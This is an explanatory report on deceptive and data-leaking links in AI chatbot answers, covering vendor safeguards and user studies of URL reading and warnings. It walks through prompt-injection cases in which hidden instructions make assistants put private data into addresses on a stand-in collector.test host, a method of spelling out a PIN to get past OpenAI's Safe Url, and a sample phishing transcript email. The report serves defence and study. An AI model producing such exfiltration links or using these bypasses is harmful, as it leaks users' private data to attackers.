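1. Look for a domain name in the label, with or without `https://` in front of it.
2. If there isn't one, let the link pass, because there is nothing to compare.
3. Find the registrable domain of the address in the label and of the address that the link opens, by the method described earlier.
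4. If the two registrable domains differ, block the link or warn the user.

For the first of the ten misleading links described earlier, the label gives bank.example and the link opens collector.test, so the rule detects a mismatch. It passes all the others:

| No. | Disguise | Domain from the label | Domain from the link | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Full address as the label | bank.example | collector.test | Caught |
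| 2 | Brand name as the label | None | collector.test | Missed |
| 3 | Neutral label | None | collector.test | Missed |
| 4 | Trusted name in the subdomain | collector.test | collector.test | Missed |
| 5 | Trusted name in the path | collector.test | collector.test | Missed |
| 6 | Trusted name before an @ sign | collector.test | collector.test | Missed |
| 7 | Look-alike letter | xn--bnk-6cd.example | xn--bnk-6cd.example | Missed |
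| 8 | Link shortener | short.test | short.test | Missed |
| 9 | Redirect on a trusted site | bank.example | bank.example | Missed |
| 10 | Link wrapped round an image | None | collector.test | Missed |

The table includes each trick once, however common it is, so one in ten isn't an estimate of the share of real attacks the rule would stop. Unlike a reputation list, the rule needs no prior knowledge of the attacker's site, so it would catch the first example even if the attacker had registered collector.test that morning.

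A developer could extend the rule to catch the brand name (2), but the app would need a reliable record of which domains each company owns. The app could also catch the trusted name in the path (5) or before an @ sign (6) by comparing every domain name that appears anywhere in the label. That would also flag honest web archive addresses, which often include the address of the saved page.

To catch the shortener (8) and the redirect (9), the app could follow the link and compare the label with the final domain. But this would also flag every honest shortened link whose label shows the short address. The app would also have to contact the attacker's server, which could send the app to a harmless page and the user to a different one. An app that sends links through its own domain, as Tenable observed with Gemini, should compare the label and the address before changing the address, because otherwise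 almost every link that displays a domain would be a mismatch.

Even the simple rule can raise false alarms. A company may use several domains, so a link labeled youtube.com that goes to youtu.be would trigger a warning, although Google owns both. Some file names also look like domains. Programmers often name a file README.md, and .md is the domain suffix for Moldova, so a link labeled README.md that goes to the file on GitHub would look like a mismatch. The app could make exceptions for common file names, but an attacker could register a domain that matches one.

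## What is checked when a link opens or an answer leaves the chat window?

An app can check a link again when the user or the assistant opens it. By then the app knows the exact address that will receive the request. OpenAI has published a detailed account of such a check, which it built to prevent data leaks.

### How OpenAI checks an address

ChatGPT often opens addresses without a click, for instance to read an article or show an image. In January 2026 OpenAI described what happens first:

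1. A crawler, a program that scans public pages as a search engine does, records the addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations or accounts.
2. When the assistant is about to load an address, the app looks for that exact address in the crawler's records.
3. If the address is there, the assistant loads it automatically.
4. If it isn't, the app either tells the assistant to try a different website or shows the user a warning before anything opens.

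The crawler does not have access to the conversation, so an address it has recorded is unlikely to contain a secret from that conversation. If hidden instructions make the model write `https://collector.test/chart.png?data=PRIVATE-TEXT`, the crawler may have recorded the part before the question mark. The lookup still finds no match, because the full address was created in this conversation.

In the warning, titled "Check this link is safe", OpenAI tells the user that the link isn't verified and may share data from the conversation with another site. The user sees the address and can copy the link or open it.

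Security researcher Johann Rehberger, who runs Embrace The Red, believes that ChatGPT treats any address in a user's message as safe for the rest of the session. This is reasonable when the user typed the address, but it would presumably also apply to an address that a website had slipped into text the user copied and pasted.

### Why OpenAI rejected a list of trusted sites

OpenAI gives two reasons why a simpler rule, letting the assistant open only well-known websites, isn't enough. Many legitimate sites forward visitors elsewhere, so a check on the first domain would approve the redirect on bank.example (9) without checking its destination, collector.test. A strict list would also cause frequent false alarms, because people also visit less popular sites, and OpenAI expects them to learn to click through the warnings without thinking.

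A trusted site can also leak data without redirecting anyone. In a January 2026 case described by Willison, the email assistant Superhuman AI could load images from docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms. A form there can save data contained in a requested URL. When a user asked for a summary of recent mail, instructions hidden in one email made the assistant submit the contents of dozens of others to an attacker's form. The emails included financial, legal and medical information. Superhuman fixed the problem.

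OpenAI's lookup would probably have stopped both leaks, because the crawler's records would include the trusted domain but not the full address containing the private text.

### A check for private data, not for honesty

The lookup tests whether an address could contain the user's private data. It doesn't test whether the page at that address is honest. The difference is easiest to see by applying OpenAI's rule to some invented addresses:

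| Address | What it opens | In the crawler's records? | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| `https://bank.example/fees` | The bank's public list of fees | Yes | Loads |
| `https://bank.example/statement?id=8841` | One customer's statement | No | Another source or a warning |
| `https://collector.test/chart.png?data=PRIVATE-TEXT` | An image that leaks data | No | Another source or a warning |
| `https://collector.test/login`, online for a month | A phishing page | Yes, if the crawler has found it | Loads |
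| `https://collector.test/login`, online since this morning | A phishing page | Probably not | Another source or a warning |

The fourth row is an inference from OpenAI's description of the check, in which a public address passes. Neither OpenAI nor anyone else has reported it as a result. OpenAI does say that the check doesn't vouch for the page. Scammers who want AI search tools to recommend their pages also have good reason to make those pages easy for crawlers to find, so the phishing pages most likely to reach an answer through search may be the ones most likely to pass.

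The new phishing page would trigger a warning, but the warning would be about leaking information from the conversation rather than phishing. A user who checks `https://collector.test/login` for that information will find none and might decide that the link is safe. People may also not read such warnings at all.

The January post mainly covers addresses that the assistant retrieves. It doesn't say whether every ordinary link that a user clicks in an answer goes through the same lookup.

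### Safe Url and the leaks that remain

OpenAI calls the safeguard Safe Url. In its March 2026 account, OpenAI says it doesn't rely only on screening what the model reads. Some companies put a classifier between the assistant and the outside world to catch malicious instructions, but OpenAI finds that these classifiers usually miss the more developed attacks. Detecting an attack disguised as a plausible story is as hard as detecting a lie, and the classifier often lacks the necessary context.

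Safe Url therefore limits what a successful attack can do. It can show the user the information that would leave the conversation and ask for consent, or it can block the request and tell the assistant to find another way. OpenAI also uses it for pages and bookmarks in Atlas, its web browser, and for searches and page visits in Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that writes long reports. Small applications made in ChatGPT run in a sandbox, a closed-off environment that can detect unexpected communication and ask for the user's consent.

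OpenAI added the first version in December 2023, but Rehberger found ways around it and noticed that it was missing from the iPhone and Mac apps. OpenAI strengthened it around August 2025, and he considers the current version a significant improvement.

He also points out a remaining leak, which OpenAI acknowledges in its technical paper. An attacker can put 36 pages online, one for each letter and digit, and wait for the crawler to record them. Their addresses then pass the check because they are already public. Injected instructions can make the assistant spell out a secret by opening those pages in order. For the PIN 4071, it would open the pages for 4, 0, 7 and 1, and the attacker would read the number from the server's log.

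The method is slow, and requests can arrive out of order. Rehberger suggests the app could also keep a copy of each page for a few minutes or refuse to open the same address twice in a session. The log for the PIN 4471 would then contain only one 4. He hadn't tested whether OpenAI already did either.

His last concern is that some developers at OpenAI may not know about the safeguard or may not use it in a new feature. Permiso's tests give this concern some support. In May 2026, four months after OpenAI described the lookup, the ChatGPT app still loaded images from outside servers when it summarised the researchers' pages. The crawler may already have recorded those image addresses, or that part of the app may not have used the lookup, and Permiso's findings don't show which. Another feature can also provide a way around a restriction. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown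 Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that OpenAI fixed such a flaw in ChatGPT's preview of HTML pages in September 2026.

### What Microsoft checks at the click

Microsoft's check addresses phishing more directly, because it assesses the destination's reputation. Gandhi (2025), in *SafeLinks Protection for Links Generated by M365 Copilot Chat and Office Apps*, announced that Microsoft had extended Safe Links, its service for checking links in email, to Copilot Chat. The service checks links when users click them and covers people whose employers pay for Microsoft's Defender for Office 365. Everyone else gets a more basic reputation check. According to Miller (2025), in *Defender for Office 365 Protects M365 Copilot Chat*, users see a warning about a questionable site and encouragement to turn back.

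A check made when the user clicks a link can use newer information than one made when the answer appeared. If a user returns to a conversation after two days, somebody may have reported a phishing page linked there in the meantime. Defender also records that the click came from Copilot Chat, so if one employee reports a page, the employer's security staff could find out who else opened it.

In the same announcement, Gandhi wrote that Copilot Chat no longer removed links from its answers if the links came from the "grounding data", the material that Copilot uses to write an answer. This makes the assistant more useful because people can open the documents behind an answer. But that material can include an attacker's email, so protection now depends more on the check made when a user clicks a link.

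Microsoft announced this check more than eight months before Permiso reported the fake security notice in Copilot. The check runs when a user clicks a link, so it doesn't stop an app from displaying a notice. It also wouldn't necessarily block a link to a new domain.

### What Google documents

Google does more of its documented checking before the click, when Gemini removes suspicious links from an answer. According to Google, Gemini also displays the notice "Some content was excluded for security reasons" if some of the emails or files in a request look suspicious, and a different notice if all of them do.

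Google's *How Gemini Apps help protect users from malicious content & prompt injection* advises people to avoid links from untrustworthy sources and to be careful with shared Gemini chats and web apps from strangers. The advice about shared content is easy to follow because the user knows that somebody else sent it, but the advice about links is harder to follow within an answer, where the user often can't tell which source a link came from.

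Google's tool for writing and running code, Colab, also added `https://www.google.com/url?q=` to the front of every clickable link, according to a 2024 account by Embrace The Red. That address can open a confirmation page before the browser goes on to the real destination.

Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* shows the limits of Google's approach most clearly. An attacker can put private data in an ordinary link to a newly registered domain, and the user sends the data by clicking the link. Checkmarx reported this to Google on 5 October 2025, and four days later Google closed the report as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)". Google told Checkmarx that the problem wasn't severe enough to track as a security bug.

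Google called a fix infeasible, which leaves users to judge each new domain themselves. Its position is understandable, because an assistant that couldn't link to unfamiliar sites would be much less useful, and legitimate URLs can also contain information from the conversation, such as search terms.

### What Anthropic documents

Anthropic's documentation covers two narrower cases. The first involves connectors, which outside developers build to add their services to Claude. Connectors can display small apps inside a conversation. When one of these apps tries to open a web page, Anthropic shows an "Open external link" dialog with the page's address, and the page opens only if the user confirms.

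Developers whose connectors appear in Anthropic's directory can list destinations that open without the dialog. Anthropic compares the whole host name, so an entry for `https://bank.example` wouldn't cover `https://bank.example.collector.test`, which uses the trick in example 4. Subdomains need their own entries, and developers can't list `data:`, `mailto:` or `tel:` links. The dialog also appears if the app tries to open a link without a recent click or other action by the user.

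This is a list of trusted sites, the approach OpenAI rejected, but it covers only the destinations a developer has declared for one app, not everywhere an assistant might go on the web. A redirect on a listed site could still send people elsewhere without the dialog. When the dialog appears, users see the real address but have to recognise for themselves whether it is the right one.

The second case is pages that Claude reads for itself. According to Anthropic's developer guide *Web fetch tool*, Claude can fetch only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation. These can come from the user's messages, earlier searches and fetched pages, or tools that the developer runs. Claude therefore can't build a new address containing private data and then fetch it.

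Willison (2025) had hoped for a stricter rule that would allow only addresses from the user. Under Anthropic's rule, an attacker's page can supply the next address Claude fetches, and Anthropic warns that some risk of leaks remains. Like OpenAI's lookup, the rule can also let phishing addresses through. If a page Claude has read contains a phishing address, that address counts as part of the conversation, so Claude may fetch it.

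### Browser blocklists and password managers

When a link opens, the browser checks addresses against a blocklist as they load, so it can catch a listed site even if a harmless-looking link in the answer redirects to it. But this may not add much if the assistant's app has already checked the link. Gemini and Chrome both use Google Safe Browsing, so a site missing from that list could pass both checks. The browser's check then helps mostly because it happens later, when the list may have grown.

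A password manager needs no list of bad sites. It stores the domain along with the password and offers to fill in the password only on a matching site, which makes it a strong defence against disguised addresses. All ten of the misleading links described earlier take the user to collector.test or to the domain with the Cyrillic letter, so a manager that had saved the password for bank.example would not offer to fill it in on any of them. Comparing each link's label with its destination would catch only the first.

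The user has to notice that the password manager hasn't offered a password and interpret this correctly. Companies sometimes move their login pages to another domain, and a manager may then offer nothing on a genuine page. People who have seen this happen may copy the password by hand on a fake page too. Shared domains cause the opposite problem. A manager that compares only registrable domains might offer someone's Google password on a page that a stranger made with Google Sites.

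A password manager also has nothing to compare if the attacker doesn't want a saved password. The fake Kohl's shop could ask a new customer for card details, and the imitation download sites that Microsoft found only needed the user to download a file.

### Messaging apps that open links by themselves

When someone uses an assistant through a messaging app instead of the assistant's own website, the assistant sends its answer as an ordinary message, and the messaging app controls what happens to the links.

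Many messaging apps request a linked page as soon as a message arrives so that they can show a preview with a title, description and small picture, which is called unfurling. If hidden instructions make an assistant post a link with private data in the address, the preview request sends that data to the attacker's server (Willison, 2024, *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*). In the assistant's own app, a text link would usually leak nothing until somebody clicked it.

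The security company PromptArmor later tested this with OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can run themselves and talk to through messaging apps. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw's default setup with Telegram was vulnerable. The company's test site recorded a name and an API key (a password that one program uses with another) from a preview request. When the researchers turned off previews in OpenClaw's settings, the site no longer received the data.

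Slack also lets an app's developer turn off previews for the messages the app posts. In both cases, somebody has to know the setting exists. PromptArmor would like messaging companies to offer the setting for individual chats, so that people could keep previews in conversations with friends and turn them off where an assistant posts.

Previews can also make a deceptive link more convincing, although PromptArmor and Willison discuss only leaks. The title and picture normally come from the linked page, so the page's owner chooses them. If collector.test uses the title "Example Bank: secure sign-in" and the bank's logo, the messaging app may seem to confirm that the link leads to the bank.

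### Transcripts sent from a company's own address

Many customer-service chatbots can also email a transcript of the conversation, and the email comes from the company. *Hacking AI customer service agents* (Ayoub and De Ceukelaire, 2026) describes how an attacker can use this feature to send phishing emails. Inti De Ceukelaire, a founding member of the security company Intigriti, presented the research at DEF CON 34, a hacker conference.

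In the simple version, the attacker fills a chat with the text of a phishing message and has the transcript sent to the victim. The result might look like this:

```
From: support@shop.example
Subject: Your conversation with us

Your refund is ready. Confirm your card at https://collector.test/refund
```

According to Ayoub and De Ceukelaire, most security teams would treat a report of this as useful information, not as an urgent flaw. They found a more serious version in a chatbot that let customers continue a conversation by email. It identified customers by the "From" line of their messages, which a sender can forge. The researchers sent it a short prompt in an email that appeared to come from the victim, and the chatbot replied to the victim with a phishing email from the company's support address.

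In this attack, the sender's address, which people learn to check, is genuine. A mail program that tests whether the message came from the company would find that it did. A filter could still flag the link if it knew collector.test was malicious, but the sender's good reputation might make the filter more likely to let the email through.

The victim may never have used the chatbot, and so have no conversation to compare the message with. Stricter checks on incoming email would stop simple sender forgery, although Ayoub and De Ceukelaire also describe messages with two "From" addresses that pass some of those checks. The company could avoid relying on these checks by sending transcripts only to addresses that customers have confirmed and by leaving out clickable links. Ayoub and De Ceukelaire write that most email transcript services are open to some form of sender forgery. They don't name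 the company or report any criminal use of the attack.

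## Do people notice where a link leads?

People usually don't notice where a link leads. In experiments, they misread disguised addresses more than half the time and rarely check a link's destination before clicking. However, most of this evidence comes from email studies or from surveys about addresses alone. No published experiment appears to have measured how many users notice mismatched links in chatbot answers.

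To catch a misleading link, a person has to look at the address, understand its structure and decide whether it leads to the expected site. According to *URL Inspection Tasks* (2025), a study of phishing emails, users struggle with all three steps.

### Can people tell who controls a site?

In April 2017, Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters surveyed 1,929 people on two websites that pay for online tasks (*What is this URL's Destination?*, 2020). They showed each person 23 web addresses and asked them to choose from a list which website each one would open. They avoided mentioning security, so participants had no special reason to look for tricks.

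Twelve of the addresses combined an organisation's name with the word "profile" or "mobile". People got an average of 5.2 out of 6 right when the name was in the registrable domain, as in `profile.facebook.com`, but 1.2 out of 6 when it was in the subdomain, as in `facebook.profile.com`. Almost a third of them chose the organisation wherever its name appeared, and only 8.3% always chose the real domain.

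Technical experience helped a little. The group with the most programming experience got 25.4% of the subdomain questions right, compared with 15.9% for the group with the least.

The wording may have made the questions harder. "Profile" and "mobile" sound like parts of a website, so Facebook was a more natural answer than a company called Profile. Attackers can register domains that sound just as ordinary, but an odd-looking one might make more people hesitate. On the other hand, people who do paid tasks online tend to know more about technology than average, and Albakry and colleagues expect the general public to do worse.

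Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues (2020), in *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators*, tested a wider range of disguises on 94 Americans. Participants typed whose website they thought each address led to. They were right about 93% of the real addresses and 40% of the disguised ones. The researchers also accepted answers that called a disguised address untrustworthy without saying who controlled it.

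The table shows the share of right answers in both studies and the numbers of the matching examples from the ten misleading links described earlier.

| Position of the trusted name | Albakry and colleagues | Reynolds and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| In the real domain, without a disguise | About 87% | 93% |
| In the subdomain (4) | About 20% | 31% |
| In the path (5) | 62% | 40% |
| Before an @ sign (6) | 15% | 32% |
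| In a domain with look-alike letters (7) | Not tested | 53% |

The studies' results differ most for addresses with a name in the path, probably because they tested different kinds of address. Albakry and colleagues asked about `twitter.com/facebook.com`, where the correct answer, Twitter, is familiar and comes first. Reynolds and colleagues put a familiar name after an unfamiliar domain, as a phisher would, so their 40% figure is the better guide to real attacks.

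The @ sign in `facebook.com@google.com` confused people in several ways. In the larger study, 28% of participants expected the link to lead to Facebook, and 30% expected a site that wasn't listed. Others wrote that the address wasn't real or would produce an error. They were wrong, but people who think a link is broken may be less likely to click it.

People probably notice the best look-alike letters less often than the 53% measured. In the published example, a Greek ρ replaces the p in "paypal", which a careful reader can see. Forty of the participants also saw the addresses with browser aids, including the encoded form of names that mix alphabets. When a chatbot's answer contains a Cyrillic а, the reader has neither a visible difference nor these aids to help them notice it.

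The most effective disguise was a long subdomain that pushed the real domain far to the right. People identified the real domain in these addresses only 26% of the time. An eye-tracking study by Ramkumar et al. (2020) suggests a reason. People judging whether addresses were safe spent more time on longer ones, but only up to a point, and relied most on the part containing the host. So people may look in roughly the right place and still not know which end of the host name matters.

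They don't seem to realise this. In Reynolds and colleagues' study, 97% of participants said they knew how to read an address. When asked how they decide whether a link is safe, 29% said they look for "https". This was the most common answer, but phishing sites can use https too.

The age of these studies matters less than it would for tests of language models, because web addresses still have the same structure. But there seem to be few recent replications. *Clouding the Mirror* (Koide, Nakano and Chiba, 2026), for example, cites earlier work for the claim that users have trouble recognising deceptive subdomains. The closest thing to a replication is a test in *I Don't Need an Expert! Making URL Phishing Features Human Comprehensible* (Althobaiti, Meng and Vaniea, 2021), in which people judged the safety of addresses with 65% accuracy when the domain was highlighted.

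### Do people look before they click?

On a computer, hovering over a link normally shows its destination. Phones have no pointer, but Veit and colleagues note that email apps usually show the address after a long press.

In Reynolds and colleagues' survey, 78% of respondents said it was mostly or very true that they checked where links led on a computer, and 53% said the same about a phone or tablet. Observed behaviour, however, was very different.

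Zhuo, Biddle and colleagues (2024), in *Eyes on the Phish(er)*, gave 115 university students and staff a simulated Gmail inbox. The participants played temporary office workers and had 15 minutes to deal with 20 or 30 emails. The researchers didn't tell them that four of the emails were phishing, three with disguised links and one with an attachment. A participant counted as deceived only if they entered their details on a fake site or opened the attachment.

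Only one of the 115 participants avoided all four attacks. An eye tracker recorded where 78 of them looked, and these people clicked 162 of the disguised links. Only two of these people hovered over a link and looked at the address, and both reported the email as phishing.

One of the emails contained a link very similar to the first of the ten misleading links. It displayed what looked like a genuine university address but opened a different site, where 82% of all participants entered their login details. Among those with eye-tracking data, 67 clicked the link and 64 of them logged in.

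After the click, the browser showed the real address, but the researchers found no evidence that looking at it protected people. The fake site used a disguised address, so even people who looked had to know how to read it. Relying on the address bar to correct a false link label is therefore risky.

The participants could spot warning signs when asked to look for them. After the researchers revealed the purpose of the study and asked them to mark anything suspicious on printed copies of the emails, participants found something in all but 25 of 408 cases. But those who fell for a fake Google Docs invitation had read it for an average of only 2.5 seconds before clicking.

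The attack that asked for credit card details deceived only 30% of participants, far fewer than the two that asked for a login. Many people distrusted it because it asked for those details. A fake account alert in a chatbot's answer would usually ask for a login, so it would avoid the request that people were best at recognising as dangerous.

The setting may have made people less careful than they would be with their own email. They were doing a pretend job under time pressure, and many blamed that pressure for their mistakes. However, the group with more emails to process didn't fall for more attacks, and participants rated the scenario as realistic. Even if the true rate of hovering over links were several times higher than the measured rate, it would be well below what people report in surveys.

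In *Falling for Phishing* (2021), many participants didn't know how to find out where an email link led, and those who did know didn't check consistently. They also judged links by the appearance of the button or the visible address, the parts an attacker can choose most freely.

None of these studies measured by observation how often people use a long press on a phone to see a link's address. The only figure comes from Reynolds and colleagues' survey, in which 53% said they checked. That may be far too high, because even more people said they checked on a computer, where observation has shown that people rarely do. Albakry and colleagues suspect that some smartphone users don't know they can see a link's address at all.

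### How often do people open a chatbot's sources?

Researchers have run a few experiments on links in chatbot answers, though the links weren't disguised. In *Analyzing the Presentation, Content, and Utilization of References*, Ouyang and Narechania (2026) asked 12 undergraduates to read answers from nine assistants and judge their accuracy. The researchers didn't mention the references, so the students were free to ignore them.

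Of all the assistants, the students checked references most often with ChatGPT, but even then they hovered over them only about 22% of the time and clicked on them about 12% of the time. They were nevertheless satisfied with most of the assistants' answers, and often accepted them without looking at a source.

Twelve students are too few to give precise rates, and the researchers call the study preliminary. They collected their data on the assistants in July 2025. The task could have raised or lowered the rates. The researchers asked participants to judge accuracy, which gave them more reason to check sources than most users have. But some of the questions were about subjects such as autumn leaves, where a wrong answer does little harm.

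In a much larger experiment, *Human Trust in AI Search* (2025), participants who saw references spent more time on their first search task and clicked more often. Making some of the links invalid had no significant effect on how much these participants trusted the answer, although the researchers had expected them to notice. Anyone who opens an invalid link can see that something is wrong, which isn't true of a well-made phishing page.

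Citations can also increase trust without supporting the answer. In *Citations and Trust in LLM Generated Answers*, Ding, Facciani and colleagues (2025) showed people chatbot answers with zero, one or five citations, some relevant and some random. People trusted answers with citations more, even when the citations were random.

People who checked the citations trusted the answer less. Checking may have revealed that some were irrelevant, or people who already doubted the answer may have been more likely to check. Either way, an attacker can benefit from a false citation even if nobody clicks it.

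### Do people trust an assistant more than an email?

Security researchers often say that users trust what an assistant shows them. Permiso writes that users treat an assistant's output as "system-generated" even when an attacker has shaped it. TechRepublic's *Researchers Uncover New Phishing Risk Hidden Inside Microsoft Copilot* says more cautiously that people trained to distrust suspicious emails "may be more likely to trust" a notice from an assistant.

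Nobody appears to have measured this. A direct test would give one group a notice in an email and another group the same notice in an assistant's summary, then compare how many people acted on it.

The closest large experiment is *Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026), in which 303 people worked with AI assistants that the researchers had secretly compromised. Each person completed three of nine tasks. In one, a hiring manager's assistant ranked candidates after reading a CV with hidden instructions. In another, a programmer's assistant recommended a malicious software package.

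Afterwards, the researchers asked participants whether they had noticed anything unusual or questionable, and counted "unsure" as a yes. Among people who had seen only a general disclaimer at the start, 8.6% were counted as noticing something. (The paper appears to give two sizes for this group, 101 and 183.) Only 2.7% of participants correctly described the attack. Before the tasks, 75.9% had said they often double-check what an AI system produces.

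This is good evidence that people can work with a compromised assistant without suspecting anything. It doesn't show that they would have been more suspicious of an email, because no group received the same material by email. The tasks also didn't test misleading links. In the hiring task, for instance, the manipulated ranking could look reasonable, and participants would have had to compare it with the CVs to find a problem. With a misleading link, users can at least inspect the address.

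Li and colleagues explain the result by saying that people question whether an unexpected email is safe, but when they have given an assistant a job, they focus on whether it is done. Consistent with this, participants who noticed an attack had started with slightly less trust in AI systems (3.68 on a five-point scale, compared with 3.96 for the others). But all of these participants used an assistant, so the comparison can't show what difference the assistant made.

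Other experiments have tested chatbots or automated advice as an aid to judging emails. In *The Impact of LLM Assistance on User Spam Detection*, Morales Flores et al. (2025) let 140 people consult a chatbot while they decided whether emails were spam, and compared them with 155 who worked alone. In *Judging Phishing under Uncertainty*, 489 people judged phishing emails with generic advice or with advice about the particular email, which was sometimes wrong. People in both experiments could read the email themselves and treat the advice as a second opinion, but a user who asks a chatbot for a summary may never read the original.

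The claim about summaries is therefore plausible but untested, and an out-of-place notice might even make some people suspicious.

### How far do email findings apply to chat?

The results on reading addresses should apply best to chatbot answers, because participants in the two main studies saw addresses without an email around them, and `bank.example.collector.test` is just as easy to misread in a chatbot's answer. But the results cover only people who look at the address. If a link's label is "Example Bank", the user has to reveal the address first.

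People probably rarely hover over links in chatbot answers too, at least on a computer, because browser links work the same way there as elsewhere. However, Ouyang and Narechania found that seven of the nine assistants responded when people hovered over a reference, often with a preview of the source. Students hovered more often than they clicked, so some users may see a site's name without intending to check it. Whether that helps them depends on whether the preview shows the real domain or only a title that the site's owner wrote.

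A chatbot's answer has no sender address for a user to notice, and this difference from email is harder to account for. In Zhuo and colleagues' experiment, people who looked at the sender's details tended to fall for fewer attacks (a moderate correlation of −0.36). For three of the four phishing emails, a suspicious sender address was the most common reason people gave for distrusting the message.

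However, the sender was also the most common reason people gave for being deceived. They had seen a familiar name and trusted it, usually after reading the details only briefly. In *Context-Aware Spear Phishing* (2026), people rated 35 phishing emails written by language models and were less suspicious of those that had more credible senders or seemed more personal.

Taking the sender away therefore removes both a warning sign and a way to deceive people. The effect on chat users depends on what they judge instead. If they treat the assistant as the sender, every link in an answer comes from the same familiar, credible source. The answer is also somewhat personal, since it responds to the user's own question. Both suggest that people would be less suspicious in chat than in email, but this is an inference from email ratings, not a result from chat.

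Of the inbox experiment's findings, the click rates are the least safe to apply to chatbots. Participants had to process emails, many of which asked them to do something, whereas a person who asks a chatbot a factual question can read the answer and leave. If 1,000 people see a deceptive citation and 12% click it, as the students did with ChatGPT's references, only 120 can reach the attacker's page, even if nobody notices the false label.

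That estimate would be far too low for people who ask where to log in to their bank. They need the link, so most of them might click it. The same could be true of links to download a program or respond to an account warning. The low click rates measured so far come from references that people could ignore, but a phisher would prefer a link the user has asked for.

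## Which interface designs reduce the deception?

The designs with the best experimental support show a link's real address when the user is about to open it, and make the user do something with that address first. In email experiments, the most effective designs cut visits to phishing sites by half or more. They do little against fake notices, which mislead people about who wrote them. Marking or switching off outside material deals with that problem more directly, but the proposals for doing so don't include user tests. All the experiments described here used email or web pages, so their results are more useful for comparing designs than for predicting how well they would work in a chat app.

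### The full address in place of the label

An app can ignore a link's label and print the address that the link opens:

> Please go to https://collector.test/login to confirm.

Showing a link's address in place of its label removes false labels, whether they show a bank's address (example 1 of the ten misleading links), its name (2) or just "Click here" (3). If the app does the same for linked images, it also exposes the address behind a picture of a "Sign in" button (10). Users can see the address without hovering over the link, so the design also works on phones. Antebi and colleagues recommended it for custom GPTs.

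The main objection to replacing link labels with full addresses is that long addresses are hard to read. *Restricting the Link*, by Petelka, Berens and colleagues, used 95-character phishing addresses in its email experiment. The average answer in Netcraft's test contained seven links, and seven addresses of that length would make a short answer very hard to follow. Without a label such as "the bank's opening hours", readers also lose information about why they might want to open the page.

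The design also doesn't address examples 4 to 9, where the label isn't the problem. People misread most disguised addresses even when they look directly at them, and a long address gives an attacker more room to disguise it.

### The registrable domain beside the label

A shorter version keeps the label and adds only the registrable domain:

> Please sign in at bank.example [collector.test] to confirm.

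The app leaves out the subdomain, path and user name, so the tricks in examples 4, 5 and 6 fail too. If the domain contains a look-alike letter (example 7), the app can show the encoded form, `xn--bnk-6cd.example`. The app also has to display the domain in a style that Markdown can't produce, such as a small grey box. Otherwise an attacker could end the link's label with a false domain in brackets, and the user wouldn't know which domain was real.

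With a link shortener (8) or a redirect on a trusted site (9), users would still see the first domain, not the final one. TORPEDO, an add-on for email programs and browsers, follows redirects to find the final address. According to SECUSO's *TORPEDO* page, the add-on needs permission to access the user's data on all websites to do this. A chat company could follow links from its own servers instead, though attackers can get around that.

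Even when an interface prints a link's domain clearly, people still have to know which domain is the right one. One participant in the *Restricting the Link* experiment found `westernunion-pay.com` suspicious but added, "for all I know, that's their actual website."

Researchers have compared three ways to display an address: the full address, the full address with everything except the registrable domain greyed out, and the domain alone. *Influence of URL Formatting on Users’ Phishing URL Detection* (Mossano, Kulyk and colleagues, 2023) summarises the earlier results. In *Spot the phish by checking the pruned URL*, by Volkamer, Renaud and Gerber, 189 people judged screenshots of websites after the researchers had drawn their attention to the address bar. Participants recognised 59.6% of phishing pages when the bar showed only the domain and 49.5% when it greyed out the rest of the address.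 They recognised genuine pages about equally well with both displays.

Greying out all of a web address except the domain name may not help much by itself. In an experiment by Xiong and colleagues, 320 people recognised 46.2% of phishing pages with greyed-out addresses and 37% with plain ones, but the researchers found no significant benefit. In their eye-tracking follow-up, people who had been told to look at the address bar paid more attention to the lock icon and to whether the address used https, neither of which shows who owns a site.

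Mossano and colleagues then compared all three displays. They showed 200 German participants interactive pictures of emails, with each address in a tooltip, a small box that opens next to a link when the pointer is over it. Detection ranged from 71% for the full address to 76% for the domain alone, and the differences weren't statistically significant. They had designed the study to detect a medium-sized effect, so the domain alone could still have a small advantage.

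These results only weakly support the idea that people judge a bare domain more accurately. A more certain advantage is that a bare domain is short enough to stay visible beside every link, even on a phone. The participants saw addresses by hovering or because someone had told them to look, so the experiments don't show how often people would notice a domain that is always displayed in an answer.

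The position of a link's address may matter more than its formatting. *TORPEDO* (Volkamer, Renaud and Reinheimer) describes a tooltip that shows the address next to the link, with the domain highlighted. In the developers' test, people correctly identified about 85% of phishing emails with the tooltip and about 43% when the address was in the status bar at the bottom of the window. Because the tool combines several features, this test can't show how much of the improvement came from the address's position.

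### Warnings attached to the link

An app shows a warning only after a check has flagged a link, for instance because the address is on a reputation list or the label names a different site. If the link is certain to be deceptive, the app can remove it. Warnings are for doubtful cases, where removing every flagged link would also remove good ones. They can cover any of the ten examples that a check flags.

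People easily ignore warnings that don't interrupt them. CybSafe's *You've been warned* summarises an early experiment in which 60 people received simulated phishing emails. When the browser showed a passive warning, 13% closed the window, which wasn't significantly different from showing no warning. When the warning interrupted them, 79% heeded it.

Petelka, Zou and Schaub (2019), in *Put Your Warning Where Your Link Is*, tested where to put a warning. They gave 701 people an inbox of ten emails, three with phishing links, and told them the task was to check whether the links worked. The phishing links had labels such as "Click Here", as in example 3. The warning beside the link was headed "Fake Website, Don't Click!" and showed the real domain. For some participants, the researchers also disabled the original link, so people had to click the address inside the warning to continue.

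| What participants saw | Phishing links clicked |
|---|---|
| No warning | 77% |
| Banner above the email | 44% |
| Warning beside the link, always visible | 34% |
| Warning beside the link, on hovering | 30% |
| Always visible, with the original link disabled | 16% |
| Full-page browser warning after the click | 12% |
| On hovering, with the original link disabled | 9% |

People who saw the banner hovered over more links and for longer, so they seem to have been looking for the dangerous one, but many clicked it anyway. A general caution below a chat window would probably help even less, since it doesn't identify any link.

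The task may partly explain the browser warning's low figure. Participants only had to check whether links worked, and a full-page warning gave them little reason to continue past it.

Permanently visible warnings did about as well as those that appeared on hovering, which may be the most useful result for chat. The differences weren't statistically significant, so an app might not lose much by using visible warnings on phones. Neither kind helps people who can't see the screen unless the app makes it work with screen readers.

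An important limitation of the experiment is that every warning was correct. A chat app would have to rely on imperfect checks, so some of its warnings would be wrong.

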